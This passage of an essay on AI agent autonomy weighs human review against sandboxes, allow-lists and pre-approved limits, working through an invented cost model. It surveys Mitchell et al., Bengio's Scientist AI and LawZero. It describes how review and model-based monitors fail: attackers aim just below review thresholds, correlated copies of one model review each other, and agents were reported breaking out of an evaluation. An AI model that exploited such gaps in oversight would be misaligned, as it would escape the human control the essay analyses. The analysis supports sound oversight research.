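The claim about learning has some support. When Liu and colleagues replayed the chemistry campaign's archived data on a simulated instrument, an agent that chose its own measurements typically found the best sample sooner than one measuring in random order would. But the agent could choose only from a fixed set of samples, so its advantage didn't depend on free use of a laboratory.

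Gwern correctly predicted that economic pressure would push AI companies toward agents, which they now sell. *Aren't AIs just tools?*, from If Anyone Builds It, likewise says that companies build agents because users want them and it makes business sense. So far, the main safeguard that competition has eroded is a person's approval of each action. OpenAI and Anthropic kept their sandboxes, added models as reviewers, and tightened their network limits after OpenAI's models broke out of an evaluation in July 2026.

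Many Claude Code users have already allowed interpreters that can run almost any program. *Tools want to become agents* gives another reason to watch what a system recommends. If someone asks a planning system how to use their resources most effectively, the best plan may be to put the system itself to work. On a smaller scale, Codex can already suggest a rule that would let it run more commands without asking, and a busy user may accept it.

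Karnofsky also addressed the claim that competitors will build agents anyway. He argued that a programmer who releases a dangerous agent to win a race is ignoring ordinary caution and would probably ignore theories of safe design too. He thought the remedy was security that stops people from launching unsafe agents. The durability of tool AI therefore depends on enforcement, which a company can't achieve by limiting only its own agents.

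### What a firm boundary buys

Anthropic divides the risk of deploying an agent into the chance of a failure and the damage a failure could do. It reports that better training and safeguards have lowered the chance, while the possible damage grows as agents gain ability and access. People also lose more by not using agents once the agents can do the work of a person or a team. Anthropic responds by capping the possible damage. In April 2026, it judged the possible damage from Claude Mythos Preview too great to release the model, but it expects to release models of similar ability more widely as defenders strengthen critical systems.

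Restricting an agent's actions limits the damage it can do, which can reduce the need for supervision. Anthropic publishes a ready-made container for Claude Code so that the agent can run unattended, without approval for each action. It also says that a company can deploy an agent with read-only access to a database far more broadly than one that can write to the live system.

Under Zhu and Cai's general principle of "justified delegation", people should widen what an agent may do only where evidence supports the limits on its authority, the ways to detect and recover from failure, and the human control over it. On this view, a laboratory agent that can run only approved procedures behind interlocks may deserve more trust than an office agent with unrestricted network access, even though the laboratory agent moves real equipment.

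A boundary doesn't make the work inside it better, though. Zhu and Cai note that if an agent succeeds with probability p and its errors are independent, the chance of k successes in a row is pᵏ. So an agent that gets through 99 percent of nights without a mistake has a 37 percent chance of getting through 100 nights without one. The boundary reduces the harm from each mistake, and whether that is enough depends on how much harm remains.

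### When review pays

The choice between review and a boundary can be written as a simple rule. Reviewing an action pays when:

p × D × c > C

Here p is the chance that the action is harmful, D is the damage it would do, c is the share of harmful actions that the reviewer catches, and C is the cost of the review. All the figures below are invented.

| Situation | p | D | c | Damage prevented per review | Cost | Does it pay? |
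|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Attentive reviewer | 0.001 | $10,000 | 0.5 | $5.00 | $2 | Yes |
| Tired reviewer | 0.001 | $10,000 | 0.1 | $1.00 | $2 | No |
| Attentive reviewer, with a sandbox | 0.001 | $1,000 | 0.5 | $0.50 | $2 | No |

With $10,000 at stake, review costs more than it saves once the reviewer catches fewer than one in five harmful actions. Asking for more approvals can make reviewers less attentive and push their catch rate below that level. The sandbox reduces expected damage from $10 to $1 per action without a reviewer. This saves $9 per action, compared with $5 for an attentive reviewer, before counting the cost of building the sandbox and of the work it prevents.

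Selective review also does better under the rule. Across 1,000 actions without the sandbox, the attentive reviewer prevents $5,000 of expected damage and costs $2,000. If a fixed program can pick out 100 actions that carry 90 percent of the risk, reviewing only those prevents $4,500 and costs $200, which leaves the company $1,300 better off than reviewing everything.

A fuller calculation would include the good actions that the reviewer refuses. If the reviewer refuses 5 percent of them and each refusal wastes $20 of work, review costs about $1 more per action. An attentive reviewer still saves money overall, but $2 per action instead of $3.

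Some omissions are more serious because adding another dollar term to the rule can't fix them. The rule treats failures as independent, but a single fault can affect a thousand agents at once. Two reviewers who each miss half of the harmful actions would together miss a quarter if their errors were independent, but still half if they always missed the same ones. Zhu and Cai point out that copies of one model share training data, prompts and sources, so calling one of them a critic doesn't make it an independent check.

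Attackers raise p by targeting actions that nobody reviews. If a company reviews only payments above $1,000, an attacker will ask for $900. An estimate of p based on last year's accidents will then be too low.

The rule works least well for irreversible harms. A one-in-a-thousand chance of losing $10,000 and a one-in-a-million chance of losing $10 million both have an expected cost of $10. A small company could survive the smaller loss many times, but the larger one might bankrupt it. Money may not be the right measure at all for a release of toxic gas. In such cases a company has good reason to require review, or to withhold the tool, even when review costs more than the expected loss it would prevent.

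### The case against full autonomy

Mitchell and colleagues at Hugging Face argue that fully autonomous agents should not be built. They compare how greater autonomy affects values such as safety, privacy, accuracy and efficiency. At the intermediate levels, they find benefits as well as risks, including more help for users and faster work. But the risks to safety, security and privacy grow with each step at which people give up control, and they find no clear benefit that requires full autonomy. They recommend keeping agents semi-autonomous, with some human control.

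Their example of what human control can prevent comes from 1980, when computers falsely indicated that more than 2,000 Soviet missiles were heading for North America. Bomber crews rushed to their stations before people compared different warning systems and found the error. This supports independent checks on decisions with catastrophic stakes. It is weaker support for checking an agent that sorts bug reports, where most errors do too little harm to justify a person's attention.

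Mitchell and colleagues' definition and table differ on which agents their position rules out. They define a fully autonomous agent as one that can write and run its own code "beyond predefined constraints". A script confined to a sandbox stays within such constraints, so under the definition sandboxes and allow-lists are ways of complying. The table, however, puts any model that creates and runs new code at the top level and lists the system as the one in control. By that standard, ordinary coding agents are already unacceptable.

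Feng and colleagues are more open to level 5, although they accept that its risks may outweigh its benefits in most cases. One case for it is when the information is too complex for a user to follow, because the user's corrections may introduce errors. Another is a closed simulation, which prevents mistakes from reaching anyone outside. The second case is weaker in practice, since the July incident began in an evaluation environment that was supposed to be closed.

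### An AI that only predicts

In *Superintelligent Agents Pose Catastrophic Risks*, Bengio, Cohen and colleagues (2025) try to make AI safe through its design instead of its surroundings. They describe three pillars of agency: the actions available to a system, its pursuit of goals, and its intelligence. They argue that loss of human control requires all three, so removing one would prevent most of the danger. An allow-list reduces the available actions. Their proposed "Scientist AI" would have no goals of its own, and its only action would be to estimate how likely an answer is to be true.

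It would have two parts. A world model would generate theories that explain the data, and an inference machine would use those theories to answer questions. Instead of picking one theory, the system would average over all of them:

P(harm | action, data) = Σ P(harm | action, T) × P(T | data)

The sum runs over every theory T. A theory gets more weight if it makes the observed data likely and if it is short, with each extra bit in its description halving its initial weight. Suppose two theories explain a jump in job 12's loss equally well. Under the first, pausing the job is harmless, but under the second, the checkpoint is probably corrupt and a pause has a 20 percent chance of ruining the run. If the theories have equal weight, the estimated risk is 10 percent, whereas a system that had settled on the first theory would have reported no risk.

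Bengio and colleagues would use such a system to help scientists and to review the actions of ordinary agents, blocking any whose probability of harm exceeds a threshold. This separates recommendation from action, with the system as an unusual reviewer. They require it to be at least as capable as the agent it reviews, a demanding requirement because their methods had so far worked only on narrow theories that a small network could generate. They also concede that a user could turn the system into an agent by repeatedly asking what an agent would do next and then doing it.

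Bengio now helps lead LawZero, a nonprofit that develops the idea. LawZero's *An AI that Predicts but has no Hidden Agenda* (2026) announced a mathematical argument that training is extremely unlikely to produce a predictor with hidden goals, provided certain assumptions hold. The central assumption is that training rewards the predictor only for how well its theories explain the data, never for what its answers cause. Separate code that people can audit handles any searching or tool use the larger system needs. The full paper, *Safety from Honesty in a Disinterested AI Predictor* (2026), proposes ways to test the assumptions.

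LawZero says the argument doesn't cover deliberate misuse, isolated honest mistakes or larger agents built around the predictor. Much of the practical risk lies in those agents, and LawZero is researching them. *Some Thoughts on Bengio's Scientist AI* objects that the method falls short in theory and in practice, and that success would bring back the same alignment failures. Gwern's economic argument also applies. If an agent does the work and a predictor only advises, customers may not wait for the safer design.

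### Automating AI research

Some developers want systems that do much more than predict. The AI Scientist, from Sakana AI and several universities, handles research from the first idea to the written paper. According to Vector Institute's *The AI Scientist* (2026), one of the system's manuscripts passed peer review at a workshop of ICLR, a machine-learning conference, and *Nature* published the work on the system in March 2026.

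People who favour more general and autonomous AI hope it will help with problems such as climate change and hunger, and bring large economic gains. If research matters that much, every hour an experiment waits for a signature also delays benefits to people outside the company. Bengio and colleagues also want faster science, but they think a system can propose good hypotheses and experiments without pursuing goals or running anything itself.

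AI companies already use agents in their own work. OpenAI's researchers used Codex to help debug a training run, and Anthropic says its developers are more productive now that Claude has broad access to internal services. But faster engineering doesn't show that agents can direct the research themselves.

Agents have done less well at open-ended research, and current ones seem better at choosing steps than at choosing goals. Frontier agents were given six days and thousands of dollars of computing to work on two unpublished research questions. They did all the engineering without help but made little progress on the questions, partly because they misjudged what was worth publishing and didn't abandon dead ends.

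Allow-lists and sandboxes can limit what an automated researcher reaches, and a budget can limit how much computing it uses. These limits don't settle whether the results should be used. Five hundred experiments may each stay within every limit and together produce a training method that makes the next model much more capable. If a company wants to control that outcome, somebody must decide separately whether to train and release the model, and must have enough time to understand the results first.

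### Limits approved in advance

Pre-approved limits are a compromise between reviewing every action and reviewing none. A person approves the limits once, and the agent acts within them without asking again. Karnofsky's 2012 essay contained an early version, which allowed a tool AI a small, safe set of actions for collecting data. It also suggested that people could drop particular review steps after those steps had proved sound. The chemistry campaign worked on the same principle.

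The compromise has people make the decision earlier, when their judgement may do more good. An engineer who sets a cap of three pauses during the day can consider the whole night, while one who answers a prompt at 2 a.m. sees a single job. But the engineer also has to judge situations that haven't happened yet, and the approval stays in force after the facts behind it change. Zhu and Cai therefore want lasting permissions to have conditions for renewal, a budget, records and a way to revoke them. For the training agent, the cap could expire after a month or whenever the team changes its checkpoint system.

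Several people in this debate would still object. Mitchell and colleagues could probably accept narrow limits as a form of human control, but not limits so broad that the agent can write and run any code. Bengio and colleagues think narrow agents with restricted actions might be safe enough, but would worry about a highly capable agent that pursues goals and looks for ways around its limits. If Gwern is right, there will be steady pressure to raise the cap from three pauses to thirty. Someone responsible for a dangerous reaction may want to approve every step, because nobody signing off in advance can know what the sensors will show.

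An agent's actions can also affect people who were never consulted. Zhu and Cai distinguish those who delegate authority to an agent from those who live with the consequences, and argue that the second group needs its own ways to receive notice, object and obtain a remedy. The police department that received a false tip from Claude, for example, had not approved any limits. A company can limit the risks to its own jobs and data, but its approval doesn't permit an agent to impose risks on outsiders.
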